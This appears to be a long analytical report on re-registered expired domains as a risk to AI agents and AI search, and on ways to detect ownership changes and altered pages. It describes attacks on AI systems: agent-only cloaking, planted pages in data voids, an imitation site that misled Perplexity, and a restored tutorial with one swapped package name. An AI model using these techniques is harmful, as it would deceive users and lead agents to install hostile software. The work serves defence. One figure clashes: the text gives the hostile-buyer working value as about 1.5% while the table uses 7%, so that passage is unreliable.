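A model can be good at spotting malicious sites when it is asked to look for them. Muzammil and colleagues built one version of their classifier using only GPT-4o's assessments of re-registered sites. It caught 97% of the malicious sites in their test, though about one in six of its alarms was false. But GPT-4o was given a screenshot, the page's code and instructions to look for threats. An agent trying to fix a Python error may not check whether the site has been sold.

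Zhang's results are less encouraging. Zhang gave an open model, Qwen3-32B, the text and address of each response and asked what kind of page it was. The model caught 57% of the responses that lacked the requested content. It caught 77% of the 30 error pages and substitutes, but most of those came from made-up addresses Zhang used as a test. Another detector wrongly flagged articles that had moved to a new address. Zhang notes that a detector can't tell a moved article from a substitute without information about what the original address should return.

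An agent that opens pythonporch.example for the first time usually has no earlier copy to compare it with, and remembering the lecturer's tutorials would do little to help it spot a near-perfect copy.

The new owner can also use cloaking. *A Whole New World* (2025), which proposes an attack rather than surveying real sites, argues that a site can reliably recognise browsing agents by their fingerprints and show them a page no person will see. Antipov reports that AIR Security found real sites that showed bots and ordinary browsers different content. A student who checks the agent's source on such a site would find a harmless tutorial and might conclude that the agent had misread it.

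### What they read changes what they say or do

Most of the malicious sites that Muzammil and colleagues' classifier newly identified were about gambling. An agent researching a Python error will probably ignore a casino page, which contains nothing useful to it, and open another result. The same seems true for most questions, and this removes much of the apparent risk.

It fails when the question is about gambling, as Brockbank's questions to ChatGPT were. It can also fail when a page contains instructions for the agent, because such a page can redirect the task without answering the user's question. But current models usually refuse such instructions, and organised attempts seem uncommon. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* reports that neither Google nor the security company Forcepoint found sophisticated, coordinated campaigns. Forcepoint did find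 the same injection templates on several domains, which it takes as a sign of organised tools.

The objection also depends on buyers continuing to publish what they publish now. Casino operators want human visitors or better search rankings. Someone who wanted to influence coding agents would publish a page about code, and Hertz's experiment showed that agents will install a stranger's package when it appears to fit the task.

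*Data-Void Exploits in Web-Searching LLMs* (2026) offers a way to measure a planted page's influence. Researchers published pages on subjects with little other coverage on the web, then questioned several chatbots every day. They recorded whether each answer cited the planted page, used its content, merely listed it or left it out, since an assistant can list a hijacked page among its sources without taking anything from it. The study cost $1,080. Google indexed the more visible pages within 48 hours, and ten days after launch, crawlers associated with AI companies had found the most visible ones. A stranger's new text could therefore be available to AI systems in under two weeks.

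### Why the human rates do not transfer

Even if all four premises hold, the rates that So and colleagues measured for people and old software do not apply to agents. AI fetchers were not yet in common use during the study, and its bot filters would have removed most of them anyway.

A fetcher that identified itself as a bot would have been easy to remove by name. A fetcher that identified itself as an ordinary browser but downloaded only the page's text would not have run the fingerprinting script, and a fetcher running in a data centre might have shared an IP address with a scanner.

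An agent controlling a full browser would have run the script, and the study could have counted it as a person. A tool that identified itself as neither a browser nor a bot could have passed the study's checks by requesting one of the site's former pages.

The study's trust figures therefore give neither a maximum nor a minimum for agents. Agent traffic could be far lower than those figures suggest if AI systems rarely follow old links, or far higher if they often do, because the filters would have counted most of it as bot traffic. The bot total can't show which is true, since much of it came from scanners that would have contacted any server.

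The filters also removed search-engine crawlers, which were irrelevant to a count of the old site's users. Crawlers matter a great deal for AI systems, because a single visit can add the stranger's tutorial to an index that thousands of agents search.

Muzammil and colleagues did not filter out bots, but their DNS records would still miss some agents' lookups. An agent running on an employee's laptop would appear in the company's records, but if the assistant's developer fetched the page from its own data centre, the lookup would happen there and the records would not include it.

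### A program's persistence and a person's openness

The software clients in So and colleagues' data are probably a better model for agents than the human readers, at least for how long the traffic lasts:

| | Person | Ordinary software | AI agent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Source of the address | Memory, bookmarks, links, search | Usually the program's code | Search, links, documentation, the model's memory |
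| After an error | Often stops trying | Keeps trying until someone updates it | May try again in a later session |
| Reply it can use | Any readable page | Data in the expected format | Any readable page |
| Possible sign of a new owner | Unexpected appearance or content | A reply in the wrong format | Content that does not fit the task |

An agent that encounters an error may have no record of it the next day, and other users' agents will not have learned from it either. As with the Android library, the traffic can continue until someone corrects the source of the address.

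An agent is easier to exploit than the Android library in another respect. A new owner may have trouble working out what reply an old program expects, as So and colleagues point out, but an agent needs only a page it can read, which a web archive may provide. However, the library contacted its domain whenever an app told it to, while an agent visits only if someone asks a suitable question and the old address is among the pages it chooses. The Android domain's steady traffic therefore does not guarantee steady traffic from agents.

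### A rough estimate of exposure

With no measured rate for agents, the best available substitute is a product of six factors:

**Expected affected answers = queries × pages considered per query × share of those pages on lapsed domains × chance of a hostile buyer × chance that the agent opens the page × chance that the page influences it**

The table is for an organisation whose assistants handle 100,000 queries a month. It gives a working value and a plausible range for each of the other factors. The last column shows how the monthly total changes if only that factor varies across its range.

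| Factor | Working value | Range | Affected answers a month |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pages considered per query | 10 | 3 to 113 | 2.3 to 87 |
| Share on lapsed domains | 0.55% | 0.18% to 1% | 2.5 to 14 |
| Chance of a hostile buyer | 7% | 1.5% to 50% | 1.7 to 55 |
| Chance of being opened | 20% | 10% to 100% | 3.9 to 39 |
| Chance of influence | 10% | 0.6% to 90% | 0.5 to 69 |

The working values give 1,000,000 pages considered, of which 5,500 are on lapsed domains. Hostile buyers take over the domains behind 385 of those pages, and the agents open 77 of the 385. About 8 of the opened pages change an answer or an action, which is roughly one query in 13,000.

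Several of these numbers are guesses. The range for pages considered comes from Rao and colleagues, who found that different systems cited between 3 and 113 addresses per question, but a system may consider many more pages than it cites.

The 0.55% figure is the share of sites in AIR that were dead (36 of 6,500), not the share of search results. If each of AIR's 2,000 queries returned ten results and each dead site appeared only once, dead sites would make up 0.18% of results. The upper limit of 1% is an assumption.

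The working value for the chance of a hostile buyer is about 1.5%. It is based on the assumption that 50% of the domains are bought while they still appear in search results, and on Muzammil and colleagues' finding that 13.9% of the re-registered domains in use were malicious. It excludes gambling sites, based on their share of the newly identified malicious domains. The 50% represents a future in which attackers search for such domains as systematically as AIR did.

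The chance that an assistant opens a given page is also an assumption. About two thirds of the visits that AI assistants sent to glasp.co's summary pages went to pages with no verified assistant fetch during the four weeks. Assistants can apparently recommend a page without having opened it recently, so citation counts are a poor guide to how many pages they open.

The chance of influence has by far the widest range, from 0.6% to 90%, a factor of 150. In Khodayari and colleagues' test, closed commercial models followed 0.6% of the injections, which were mostly crude. The 90% is a guess for a restored tutorial with one altered line, which gives a model almost nothing to resist. An organisation can't look up this chance, although it can count its own queries and pages.

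Multiplying averages also hides how the last factor, the chance that a page affects the answer, varies with the type of buyer. If all 77 hostile pages that the agents open are casino sites, and one in a thousand affects the answer to an unrelated question, the expected total is less than 0.1 affected answers a month. If a tenth of the 77 are instead careful copies of the old site with a 90% chance of affecting the answer, those pages alone affect about 7 answers a month. The estimate therefore depends mainly on how many buyers restore the old site and change something small.

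Nobody has measured that. Muzammil and colleagues' classifier would probably have marked the stranger's tutorial as benign, so any such copies in their data may be among the 86% of domains classed that way.

The monthly figure is also an average that few months would match. At a 7% chance of a hostile buyer per domain, only two or three of AIR's 36 domains would go to hostile buyers. The organisation might go a year without an affected answer if those domains appeared only for rare questions, but it could have hundreds in a month if one of them ranked well for a common Python error.

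## Checking whether a domain has changed owner

An ownership check tests whether a domain still belongs to whoever held it when someone linked to or cited it. Registration records rarely name the owner any more, so most checks look for a break in the registration instead.

### The creation-date rule

The simplest ownership check flags a domain if its current registration is newer than the link to it. Renewing a domain changes its expiry date but not its creation date. If the registry deletes the domain and somebody registers it again, the new record has a new creation date. Unless the old owner bought the domain back, a link made before that date pointed to a different party's site or to a name that nobody had registered yet. The check can therefore catch phantom domains as well as re-registered ones.

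Suppose a page from 2016 links to two domains. The record for the first gives a creation date in 1998. That registration predates the link and has continued ever since, so the rule doesn't flag the domain. The record for the second gives 2025. The page's author can't have meant to link to a registration that began nine years later, so the rule flags the domain. The second domain may have first been registered just as long ago as the first. The golf club's domain in the study by Muzammil and colleagues dates from 1998, but they detected it because somebody registered it again in the summer of 2025.

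Dating the link can be harder than dating the registration. In the example of the two colleges, the librarian vetted the tutorial on 12 January, the stranger registered the domain on 23 May, and the second college downloaded the page on 2 June. If the college compares the domain's creation date with its own download date, the domain passes the check because it was registered before the download. The college has to use 12 January instead, the last time a person judged the page worth including. A "last updated" date on a web page can mislead in the same way, because an editor who corrects a spelling mistake may not open the links.

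A search result has no link date, but a web archive can be checked instead. If the archive holds a copy of the site from before the current registration began, the domain name has lapsed at least once. For an address that a model produces from memory, the end of its training data is a reasonable substitute for the link date.

### Why blocking new domains is not enough

Many security filters block any domain registered in about the last 30 days, because criminals often use new domains soon after registering them. *A Longitudinal Study of Recently Observed Malicious Domains* (2026) examined 1.16 million attack domains and found that 29.9% were detected within a week of registration. But the median age at detection was 60 days, so a 30-day block would have missed more than half of the domains, including the one in ten that were more than 403 days old.

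Those figures cover attack domains of all kinds. The buyer of a re-registered domain can wait even longer, since the old links stay in place. *Domain-Z* (Lever, Walls and colleagues, 2016) studied expired domains that later turned malicious and found an average of 888 days between expiry and abuse, though part of that time may have passed before anyone re-registered the domain.

In December 2026 the two tests would give these results:

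| Link made | Current registration began | 30-day block | Creation-date rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2016 | 1998 | Allows | Allows |
| 2016 | December 2024 | Allows | Flags |
| 2016 | 2025 | Allows | Flags |
| 1 December 2026 | 20 November 2026 | Blocks | Allows |

The 30-day block depends only on the age of the current registration. A domain that someone re-registered two years ago passes, even though every link from before that date now leads to a different party. A two-year block would catch it, but would also block every legitimate site less than two years old.

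### Where the dates come from

The usual source for a creation date is RDAP, the successor to WHOIS. Fernandez, Hureau and colleagues (2024), in *WHOIS Right?*, describe how a lookup works. If the lecturer's site were a real .com, the steps would be:

1. The software downloads a public file that lists the RDAP server for each top-level domain.
2. It adds the domain name to the address of the .com server and sends the request.
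3. The registry returns a structured record that includes the creation date. The record also points to the registrar's server, which may hold more detail.

WHOIS offers much the same information as RDAP, but in plain text whose layout and even language vary. Fernandez and colleagues had to write 242 templates to extract the fields they wanted. RDAP also has separate labels for registration, re-registration and transfer, while a WHOIS "creation date" can mean different things at different companies.

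The researchers collected both kinds of record for 55 million domains in December 2022, and the creation dates disagreed for 5.7% of them. In 84% of these cases the dates were less than two days apart, which leaves about 0.9% of all domains with a larger difference. One registrar's dates were consistently a month earlier than the registry's, probably because it gave customers 30 days to cancel an order. A filter should therefore allow a margin of a few days, and treat a domain as uncertain if its records disagree about whether it is older than the link.

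An RDAP record describes only the current registration, but zone files can supply some of the history. A zone file lists the names under a top-level domain that have name servers, the computers that answer DNS queries about them. Most generic registries share their zone files daily through an ICANN service. A deleted name disappears from the file and returns after someone registers it again, so a series of daily files can reveal the gap.

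Thottungal Valapu, Jonker and colleagues (2026) combined zone files with RDAP records and their own daily DNS scans in *Zombies in Alternate Realities*. Their algorithm marks each day a domain appeared in a zone file or scan, and treats each unbroken run of days as a possible registration. If RDAP gives a creation date in the middle of a run, the algorithm splits the run there. It then joins runs less than 80 days apart, unless RDAP shows that a new registration began between them.

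The 80-day threshold is cautious because it matches the usual length of the whole expiry process. The lecturer's domain might be missing from the zone file for only 38 days, from 15 April to 23 May. Because that gap is below the threshold, the algorithm would treat the lecturer and the stranger as one owner without RDAP. The RDAP creation date of 23 May prevents this error.

### Inferring a change from DNS traffic

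Passive DNS is a stored record of the lookups that computers have made and the answers they received. It can provide clues when registration records are missing or too slow to collect. Lever and colleagues used it to build Alembic, an algorithm that looks for dates on which several things about a domain changed at once. For each candidate date it compares the days before with the days after, and adds up three scores:

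**Alembic score = change in hosting + change in lookup volume + change in the SOA record**

Each part runs from 0 to 1, so the total runs from 0 to 3.

The hosting score is one minus the share of IP addresses that appear in both periods. If a domain used addresses A and B before the date and B and C after it, one of the three addresses appears in both periods, and the score is 1 − 1/3, or about 0.67. For lookup volume, Alembic uses a t-test to check whether the average number of lookups differs before and after the date. The score is one minus the test's p-value, so a clearer difference gives a higher score. The SOA ("start of authority") record names the domain's main name server and a contact email address. A complete change in either adds half a point.

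If the stranger uses a new host, name server and email address, and the t-test gives a p-value of 0.3, pythonporch.example scores 1 + 0.7 + 1 = 2.7. But the score might have been nearly as high if the lecturer had kept the domain and moved the site to another hosting company. The algorithm therefore ranks dates worth investigating, but it can't prove that a sale took place.

Alembic also needs a fair amount of traffic. The version that Lever and colleagues tested used seven days with recorded lookups before a date and seven after it. They compared its output with 17,838 ownership changes known from old WHOIS records. Only 25.5% of the changes fell within a period that Alembic could score, even though the researchers had left out the domains with the fewest lookups. The test did not measure how often a high score was a false alarm.

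### What a valid certificate proves

A valid certificate, which a browser needs for an "https" connection, doesn't show that a site still has the same owner. A certificate authority issues the most common kind after checking only that the applicant controls the domain at that moment. The stranger controls pythonporch.example from 23 May, so they can obtain a certificate as valid as the lecturer's was.

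The lecturer's old certificate may also remain valid for a while. Thottungal Valapu and colleagues use the term "zombie linkage" for any connection between a domain and an outside resource, such as a certificate, cryptocurrency wallet or software package, that outlives the ownership it was based on. Between October 2025 and April 2026, they collected 52.2 million certificates for newly registered domains. About 2.7% of the certificates valid at a given time were zombies.

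Certificate authorities had revoked only 4.3% of the 675,000 zombie certificates that the researchers analysed in detail, and the median certificate stayed valid for 75 days after its domain lapsed. In about 7,300 cases, a server was still presenting the old certificate after someone had re-registered the domain. To exploit the old certificate, the previous holder would also need a way to divert the new owner's visitors to that server.

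These figures come from new domains, many of which lapse within weeks, so the zombie share is probably lower across the whole web. The sample also could not show takeovers of established domains like the lecturer's. A certificate is equally poor evidence that a new or established domain has kept the same owner, because the certificate authority checks that the applicant controls the domain and never compares the applicant with an earlier owner.

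A new certificate is also a weak warning sign. Many certificates last 90 days, so a legitimate site may replace its certificate four times a year. The industry's maximum certificate lifetime will fall to 47 days by 2029.

The same study examined Maven Central, a public collection of Java software that checks domain ownership only once. A publisher who proves control of a domain can claim a name based on it. Of 31,853 such names, 4,842 (15.2%) are now zombies. For 214 of these, someone published new software versions after the domain was re-registered. That could have been the original publisher, who keeps access to the account, or a new owner. Telling them apart would require comparing the software and the keys used to sign it.

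Thottungal Valapu and colleagues recommend checking ownership every time a system relies on a domain, or at least setting an expiry date for each check. If that takes too many resources, they suggest focusing checks on the first few anniversaries of a domain's registration, when most of the zombies they studied appeared.

### A registration-date policy for websites

Three of the researchers who had registered the 201 expired domains later designed a defence for websites that depend on other people's domains. *What Gets Measured Gets Managed* (So, Ferdman and Nikiforakis, 2025) describes this link integrity management system, or LiMS. The site's owner sets policies that outside resources must meet. A script in each visitor's browser intercepts requests from the site's pages and checks with the owner's server whether the resource has passed. If the resource has failed any policy, the script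 blocks the request and the server alerts the owner. The server stores the results, so it doesn't have to repeat every check for every visitor. In tests, the system added 250 to 400 milliseconds to a typical first page load and almost nothing to later ones.

One of the policies blocks resources on recently registered domains, with an age limit chosen by the owner, unless the owner has made an exception. This policy is closer to the 30-day block than to the creation-date rule, but So and colleagues note that it could be changed to single out domains that the system had seen before they expired.

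They also studied how often such a policy would interfere with ordinary links. They took 85 home pages that Common Crawl had archived in all ten of its crawls over about a year, and estimated the age of the youngest domain each page linked to. On 45 of the pages, no newer domain appeared. Most of the others added one only occasionally, as when the US Postal Service linked to a 424-day-old domain for its package lockers. The exception was kottke.org, a long-running blog that constantly links to new sites.

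These results suggest that an age limit would rarely cause problems for a typical company website, though the study did not test whether the policy stops attacks. An AI agent that searches the web is more like the blog, because it keeps visiting domains it has not visited before. For an agent, comparing a domain's registration date with the date of each link should cause fewer false alarms than a fixed age limit.

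LiMS also works only if the visitor's software runs its script. If the university installed LiMS, it could protect an agent that opened the reading list in a full browser, but not one that downloaded the list as plain text. The second agent's developer would have to build the check into the tool that opens pages.

### Changes that the rule misses

The creation-date rule detects a new registration, which is not the same as a new owner. *Game of Registrars* distinguishes four ways for a domain to change hands, and two of them leave the creation date alone:

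| How the new owner gets the domain | Creation date | Creation-date rule |
|---|---|---|
| Buys it from the current owner | Unchanged | Misses it |
| Buys it at a registrar's auction after expiry but before deletion | Unchanged | Misses it |
| Uses a dropcatching service at the moment of release | New | Catches it |
| Registers it at any later time | New | Catches it |

A domain won in an Expired Auction at the registrar Dynadot keeps its original creation date, according to the company's own help page on these auctions, which it updated in August 2025. For example, the record for a domain first registered on 1 February 2015 still shows that date after the auction.

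*Game of Registrars* gives some idea of how many ownership changes this route hides. Over four weeks in 2016, it tracked .com names that registrars were offering for sale before deletion. About 70,600 stayed registered, either because someone bought them or because the owner renewed late. Of the .com names due for deletion in the same weeks, about 334,300 had been registered again by mid-December. If all 70,600 were sales, the rule would have missed about 17% of the ownership changes in the two groups combined.

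The true share could be higher or lower, because some of the 70,600 were late renewals and the researchers did not have every registrar's sale list. The figure also excludes sales by current owners, which is likely how the most valuable domains change owner. An attacker with a large budget can therefore avoid the rule by buying a domain before it is deleted.

Alembic might detect some of these sales because it does not depend on the creation date. *Game of Registrars* says the signals would probably be too weak, since a domain's DNS may change only slightly if the domain stays with the same registrar or hosting company.

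A checker could settle many of these cases if owner names were still public. *From WHOIS to WHOWAS* (2021) traces their removal to the General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), the European Union's privacy law, and to the temporary rules that ICANN introduced in response. Without names, a checker can't see that a domain has been sold. It also can't tell when an owner has let a domain lapse by mistake and then registered it again, so the rule flags that owner's site as well as sites re-registered by strangers.

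Country-code domains may have no registration date to check. When Fernandez and colleagues counted, all generic top-level domains had an RDAP server, but only 9% of country-code ones did. Coverage may have improved since, but in 2026 Thottungal Valapu and colleagues still found no server for Estonia's .ee and no registration dates in the replies for Germany's .de. Zone files are rarely an alternative, since most country-code registries don't share them. If the lecturer's site were under .de, the rule couldn't give an answer, and a filter should record the result as unknown. If it treated a missing date as a pass, attackers could get around the check by buying domains under country codes that don't provide dates.

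Even where records are public, registries and registrars limit how fast anyone can request them. Lever and colleagues reported that WHOIS access was often restricted to fewer than 1,000 queries a day from one computer. *Game of Registrars* spaced its 2016 queries two seconds apart for .com and 30 seconds apart for .org to avoid being blocked.

The earlier estimate of exposure assumed an organisation whose assistants consider a million pages a month. Checking each page separately would take 23 days at one lookup every two seconds, and almost a year at one every 30 seconds. Many pages share a domain, so the organisation could store each domain's creation date and reuse it. However, it would have to refresh the stored dates to avoid repeating Maven Central's mistake. The expiry date in the record can help with this, because a domain is unlikely to lapse before that date.

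### Most flagged domains are harmless

A correct flag that a domain has changed owner is still weak evidence of an attack. Of the re-registered domains that Infoblox's customers looked up, Muzammil and colleagues classed 86.1% as benign and 13.9% as malicious. A filter that blocked all of them would block about six harmless sites for every malicious one. The ratio would be higher if gambling sites were not counted as malicious.

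An ownership check also misses most malicious domains. Of the domains Lever and colleagues found on public blocklists between 2009 and 2015, only 8.7% had expired and changed owners before they were listed. Attackers got the rest in other ways, such as registering new names.

The flag is more useful for judging a citation. If pythonporch.example is now a harmless shop, an agent can open it safely, but the page no longer supports the claims that cited the lecturer's tutorial. A system could reasonably let the agent read the page but remove the citation, or link it to an archived copy from before the domain lapsed.

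## Checking the page itself

An ownership check produces a list of domains that have probably changed hands, most of them harmless. To find the dangerous ones, a filter has to check whether each page looks hostile, or whether it is still the page that someone linked to. Either check would catch the slot-machine site on the golf club's old domain. The stranger's tutorial is much harder to catch because it looks harmless and closely resembles the original.

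### How EchoLoc judges a page

Most detectors of hostile pages look for phishing. EchoLoc, the system that Muzammil and colleagues used to count malicious re-registered domains, learned from re-registered domains themselves. It judges a site in five steps:

1. A scraping tool takes a screenshot and saves the page's code.
2. Software groups sites whose screenshots look alike, such as parked domains and casinos built from one template. EchoLoc examines one randomly chosen site from each group and applies the verdict to the rest, which cuts the work by 55%.
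3. GPT-4o receives the screenshot and the code, with a request to consider innocent explanations. It returns a threat score and a confidence score (each from 0 to 10), a one-word category and a short explanation.
4. Software converts five kinds of evidence into numbers: the two scores, the wording of the explanation, the category with its risk level, the look of the screenshot, and 15 features of the code, such as disguised scripts or words like "casino".
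5. A random forest, which is a large set of decision trees that vote, labels the site benign or malicious.

For the golf club's domain, GPT-4o gave a threat score of 8, a confidence score of 7 and the category "gambling". Its explanation was that modified apps from unofficial sources often carry malware.

To train the random forest, a security professional classified 2,000 re-registered domains by hand and marked 26% as malicious. The researchers then tested the forest with different sets of evidence. In the table, precision is the share of flagged domains that were malicious, and recall is the share of malicious domains that the forest flagged.

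| Evidence used | Precision | Recall | Overall accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Code and screenshot | 0.97 | 0.83 | 96.0% |
| Language model's output | 0.84 | 0.97 | 95.5% |
| Both | 0.95 | 0.95 | 98.1% |

The code and screenshot produce few false alarms but miss one malicious site in six, which is the opposite weakness to that of GPT-4o's output. Combining them with that output helps most when the threat score is about 4 to 6, because GPT-4o gave such scores to both harmless and malicious sites.

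Because of these shortcuts, a wrong verdict on one site spreads to its whole group. EchoLoc also drops any site that is still empty a week after its first visit, so a buyer can avoid detection by waiting longer to add content.

The signals the classifier learned are the bigger obstacle to detecting the stranger's tutorial. The classifier treats education as a low-risk category, so a restored programming tutorial would start in that category, contain no suspicious words and look like an ordinary blog.

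### Why precision falls when hostile pages are rare

A precision of 0.95 holds only for a mix of pages like the one in the test. If hostile pages are rarer, the classifier catches the same share of them but has many more harmless pages on which to raise false alarms:

**Precision = (recall × hostile share) ÷ (recall × hostile share + false-alarm rate × harmless share)**

If 26% of the test pages were malicious, as in the labelled set, EchoLoc's results imply that it wrongly flags about 1.76% of harmless pages. Suppose it checks 10,000 pages, of which 1% are malicious. It would catch 95 of the 100 malicious pages and wrongly flag 174 of the 9,900 harmless ones, so only 95 of its 269 alarms would be correct.

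The accuracy figures in the paper fit a test set with about 20% malicious pages better. That would put the false-alarm rate at 1.25%, which improves the results somewhat:

| Hostile share of the pages checked | Precision if the test set was 26% malicious | Precision if it was 20% malicious |
|---|---|---|
| 13.9% (re-registered domains in use) | 0.90 | 0.92 |
| 1% | 0.35 | 0.43 |
| 0.0385% (all pages in the earlier exposure estimate) | 0.02 | 0.03 |

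The last row uses the estimate that 385 of the million pages an organisation's assistants consider each month are on domains with hostile buyers. If EchoLoc checked all million pages, at least 97 of every 100 alarms would be false. If it checked only pages on re-registered domains, about nine in ten alarms would be correct, which is a strong reason to check ownership first. The calculation assumes that EchoLoc makes errors at the same rate on ordinary pages, which its makers did not test.

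### Checking the links in an answer

A filter can also examine an AI search engine's answer before the user sees it. In *Unsafe LLM-Based Search*, Luo, Peng and colleagues (2025) first measured how often such a filter would be needed. They used GPT-4o to draw five keywords from each of 100 known malicious sites, then searched for the keywords both as a list and as an ordinary question on ChatGPT Search, Perplexity, Copilot, TextCortex, Grok, Doubao and Kimi. Of the responses, 47% contained a malicious address somewhere, and 34% cited harmful content directly in the answer.

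These rates are high because the queries came from malicious sites. They measure how the engines respond when a harmful page matches the question, not how often an ordinary user encounters one. When Netcraft asked about banks and shops, only 1.7% of the answers contained a malicious link.

The engines differed more in what they cited than in what they found. When queried with keyword lists, ChatGPT Search retrieved about three malicious addresses per query, more than most of the others, but used only 13.2% of them in its answers. Perplexity used 70.7% of those it retrieved and Doubao used 67.6%, though Doubao usually added a warning. Asking about an address directly was riskier. When the researchers gave Grok 49 malicious addresses that it had previously only listed among its sources, it cited 48 of them in its answers, some with warnings.

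Google and Bing did worse than all seven AI engines in a later comparison. But the researchers had already reported the malicious sites they had found to the AI companies, which had begun to act on the reports, so the comparison may overstate the AI engines' advantage.

Luo and colleagues built a defensive agent on GPT-4.1. It reviews an answer for six kinds of risk, such as phishing and malware, sends each cited address to a detector, and adds warnings or safer alternatives. They tested three detectors on 204 addresses. They also ran the agent on 46 answers that cited a malicious site without warning, and counted an answer as repaired if it now carried a warning.

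| Detector | Malicious addresses caught, of 83 | Harmless addresses flagged, of 121 | Answers repaired, of 46 |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1, reading the address and the page's code | 67 | 13 | 36 |
| XGBoost, a classifier using 15 features of the address and site | 83 | 83 | 46 |
| PhishLLM, an existing phishing detector | 2 | 7 | 12 |
| None, only instructions to GPT-4.1 | | | 17 |

XGBoost's perfect score means little because it also flagged 69% of the harmless addresses. PhishLLM did badly partly because about half of the malicious sites were not phishing sites. The GPT-4.1 detector is the only practical choice of the three. It missed 19% of the malicious addresses. It also flagged 10.7% of the harmless ones, which Luo and colleagues call a minor loss of information.

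That loss looks more serious when hostile pages are rare. In the test, 41% of the addresses were malicious and the GPT-4.1 detector's precision was 0.84. With the same error rates, its precision would fall to 0.55 if 13.9% of pages were hostile and to 0.07 if 1% were.

Instructions alone corrected just over a third of the answers. *SafeSearch*, which ran 300 tests on 17 models, likewise found that reminding a model to be careful did not reliably help. In one setting, the most vulnerable model gave unsafe answers in 90.5% of attacks.

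The GPT-4.1 detector also has a weakness that matters especially for re-registered domains. It is instructed to treat the address as the most important evidence and to look for misspelled brand names and brands on free hosting services, but a re-registered domain is the genuine name, correctly spelled.

### Comparing a page with its archived copy

The other kind of check compares the live page with an older copy, usually from a public web archive. The copy must be from before the domain changed owners and should be from about the time someone made the link. For the tutorial, a copy from early January would be ideal, since the librarian vetted the page on 12 January.

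An exact match is too much to ask of most pages. So and colleagues cite a study that revisited tens of thousands of websites daily and found that only 3% of script addresses always returned the same content. Ordinary pages also change whenever a site updates a date, an advertisement or a list of recent articles. A useful comparison therefore concentrates on features that an owner rarely changes without a reason:

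| Feature | Redesign by the same owner | Casino takeover | Restored copy with one altered line |
|---|---|---|---|
| Layout | Different | Different | Same |
| Topic | Usually the same | Different | Same |
| Language | Usually the same | Often different | Same |
| Outgoing links | Many survive | Few or none survive | Nearly all survive |
| Commands and download addresses | Mostly the same, with newer versions | Gone | One is different |

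The takeovers that Muzammil and colleagues describe would be easy to catch by comparing a site's current topic with its earlier one. For example, weavingroom.com had hosted a site about books on clothing since 1998 and now promotes football betting in Vietnam. The former site of an academic conference, created in 2023, also carries gambling content now. The comparison would be enough in both cases, even if the classifier had never seen a betting site.

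A redesign is harder to recognise because it can change more of the page than a careful takeover does. One remedy is to measure how much the page used to change. Chen, Chen and Karray (2026) faced a similar problem in *Agent-Targeted Cloaking on the Web* when they compared the pages that websites send to AI agents and to browsers. A simple comparison of two ordinary browser visits, made within a minute or two, flagged 7.2% of sites as different. They therefore measured each page's normal variation and counted only differences beyond it, which reduced false alarms to 0.9% of sites.

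The same idea should work over years. If archived copies show that the lecturer revised the wording every summer but always wrote about Python and linked to the same documentation, a new topic is a much stronger warning sign than a new layout. A checker should also compare several pages, since a single old article may have moved during a redesign.

A redesign is probably the owner's work if the domain's registration has continued since before the link was made, but it deserves a closer look if it appears a week after a new creation date. A sharp change of topic can also reveal some sales that the creation-date rule misses, such as the sale of a domain auctioned before deletion.

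Such a comparison could mistake a redesign for a takeover. How often this would happen is unknown, because Chen and colleagues tested differences between visitors rather than between owners. The result is also "unknown" if the archive has no earlier copy of the page, which will always be the case for pages the new owner has added.

### When only one line has changed

A comparison of overall similarity fails on the stranger's tutorial. Chen and colleagues use a common measure of this kind, in which software lists every run of five consecutive words in each version and calculates what share of all the distinct runs appears in only one version.

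Suppose the tutorial has 1,000 words and the stranger changes one word, the package name. Each version contains 996 runs of five words, and the change affects five of them. If no run repeats, the versions share 991 runs out of 1,001 distinct ones, a difference of about 1%. Chen and colleagues ignore differences below 5%, so they would treat the two versions as the same. A threshold low enough to catch this change would also flag corrected spelling mistakes.

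The small change matters because it is in a part of the page that leads directly to an action. A checker can extract such parts, including installation commands, package names, download addresses, payment details and email addresses, and compare them exactly with those in an earlier copy. In the tutorial, that would leave a handful of items to compare, one of which differs from the January copy.

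A different package name doesn't prove an attack, since packages get renamed and good tutorials are updated to match. But a maintained tutorial's domain normally has an unbroken registration. If a stranger has re-registered the domain and changed the package name, the domain's creation date will be new too. An agent could reasonably refuse to install the package until it has confirmed the name with the software's makers.

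False statements in ordinary prose are harder to isolate. Luo and colleagues created a website about an imaginary species and, three weeks later, a second site that imitated it but reversed certain facts, such as changing the species' status from "Least Concern" to "Critically Endangered". The imitation also claimed to be the official website and warned readers against the original. When the researchers asked about the species on Perplexity with eight different models, Perplexity treated the imitation as authentic and warned against the original with every model.

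The experiment does not show whether the copied content or the claim to be official was more persuasive. Perplexity also had no other sources on the species, which helped the imitation. The stranger has a different advantage, which is that the lecturer's original is no longer online to contradict the copy.

A language model might catch a reversed fact by comparing the meaning of the current page with that of an archived copy, sentence by sentence. But it would have to distinguish a lie from a legitimate correction, and the archived copy shows only what the page used to say, which may itself be wrong, for example on an old medical page.

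### Why the check must use the agent's copy

All these checks assume that the checker and the agent see the same page. A web server can break that assumption by cloaking, which means choosing its response based on the name a visitor's software gives, the network it connects from, or the technical details of its browser. If a security service visits from its own machine, the server can send it the clean tutorial and send the agent the altered one. The service's verdict may not apply to the page the agent read, even if it is correct for the page the service saw.

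*A Whole New World* proposes an agent-only attack that worked with all three models in a test on a small internal website. The test shows that the attack is feasible but doesn't measure how common it is.

In October 2026, Chen and colleagues tested whether 4,705 popular sites sent different pages to AI systems than to ordinary browsers. They made paired requests that differed only in the name of the visiting software. The sites sent ChatGPT-User the same page as an ordinary browser in 74% of cases, a different page in 5% and a refusal in 21%. Most of the different pages were not aimed at AI systems in particular, since an unknown bot got similar treatment.

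Across all the AI names tested, only four sites addressed AI systems in text that browsers did not receive. Three offered documentation or an introduction to it. The fourth, a major news publisher, added a bank's sponsored text to the pages it sent to AI agents.

These figures are weak evidence about re-registered domains, whose buyers may have more to hide than popular websites do. The researchers also could not send their test requests from the AI companies' networks, so they may have missed pages that a site shows only to verified agents.

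A filter should therefore save the response that the agent received and check that copy. If another model condenses the page first, as happens with Claude's WebFetch, the filter has to check the page before that model reads it, because that model is also exposed to the page. For a stored collection, the filter should check the exact text about to be indexed. The second college should examine what it downloaded on 2 June, since the stranger can restore the right package name before anyone inspects the live page.

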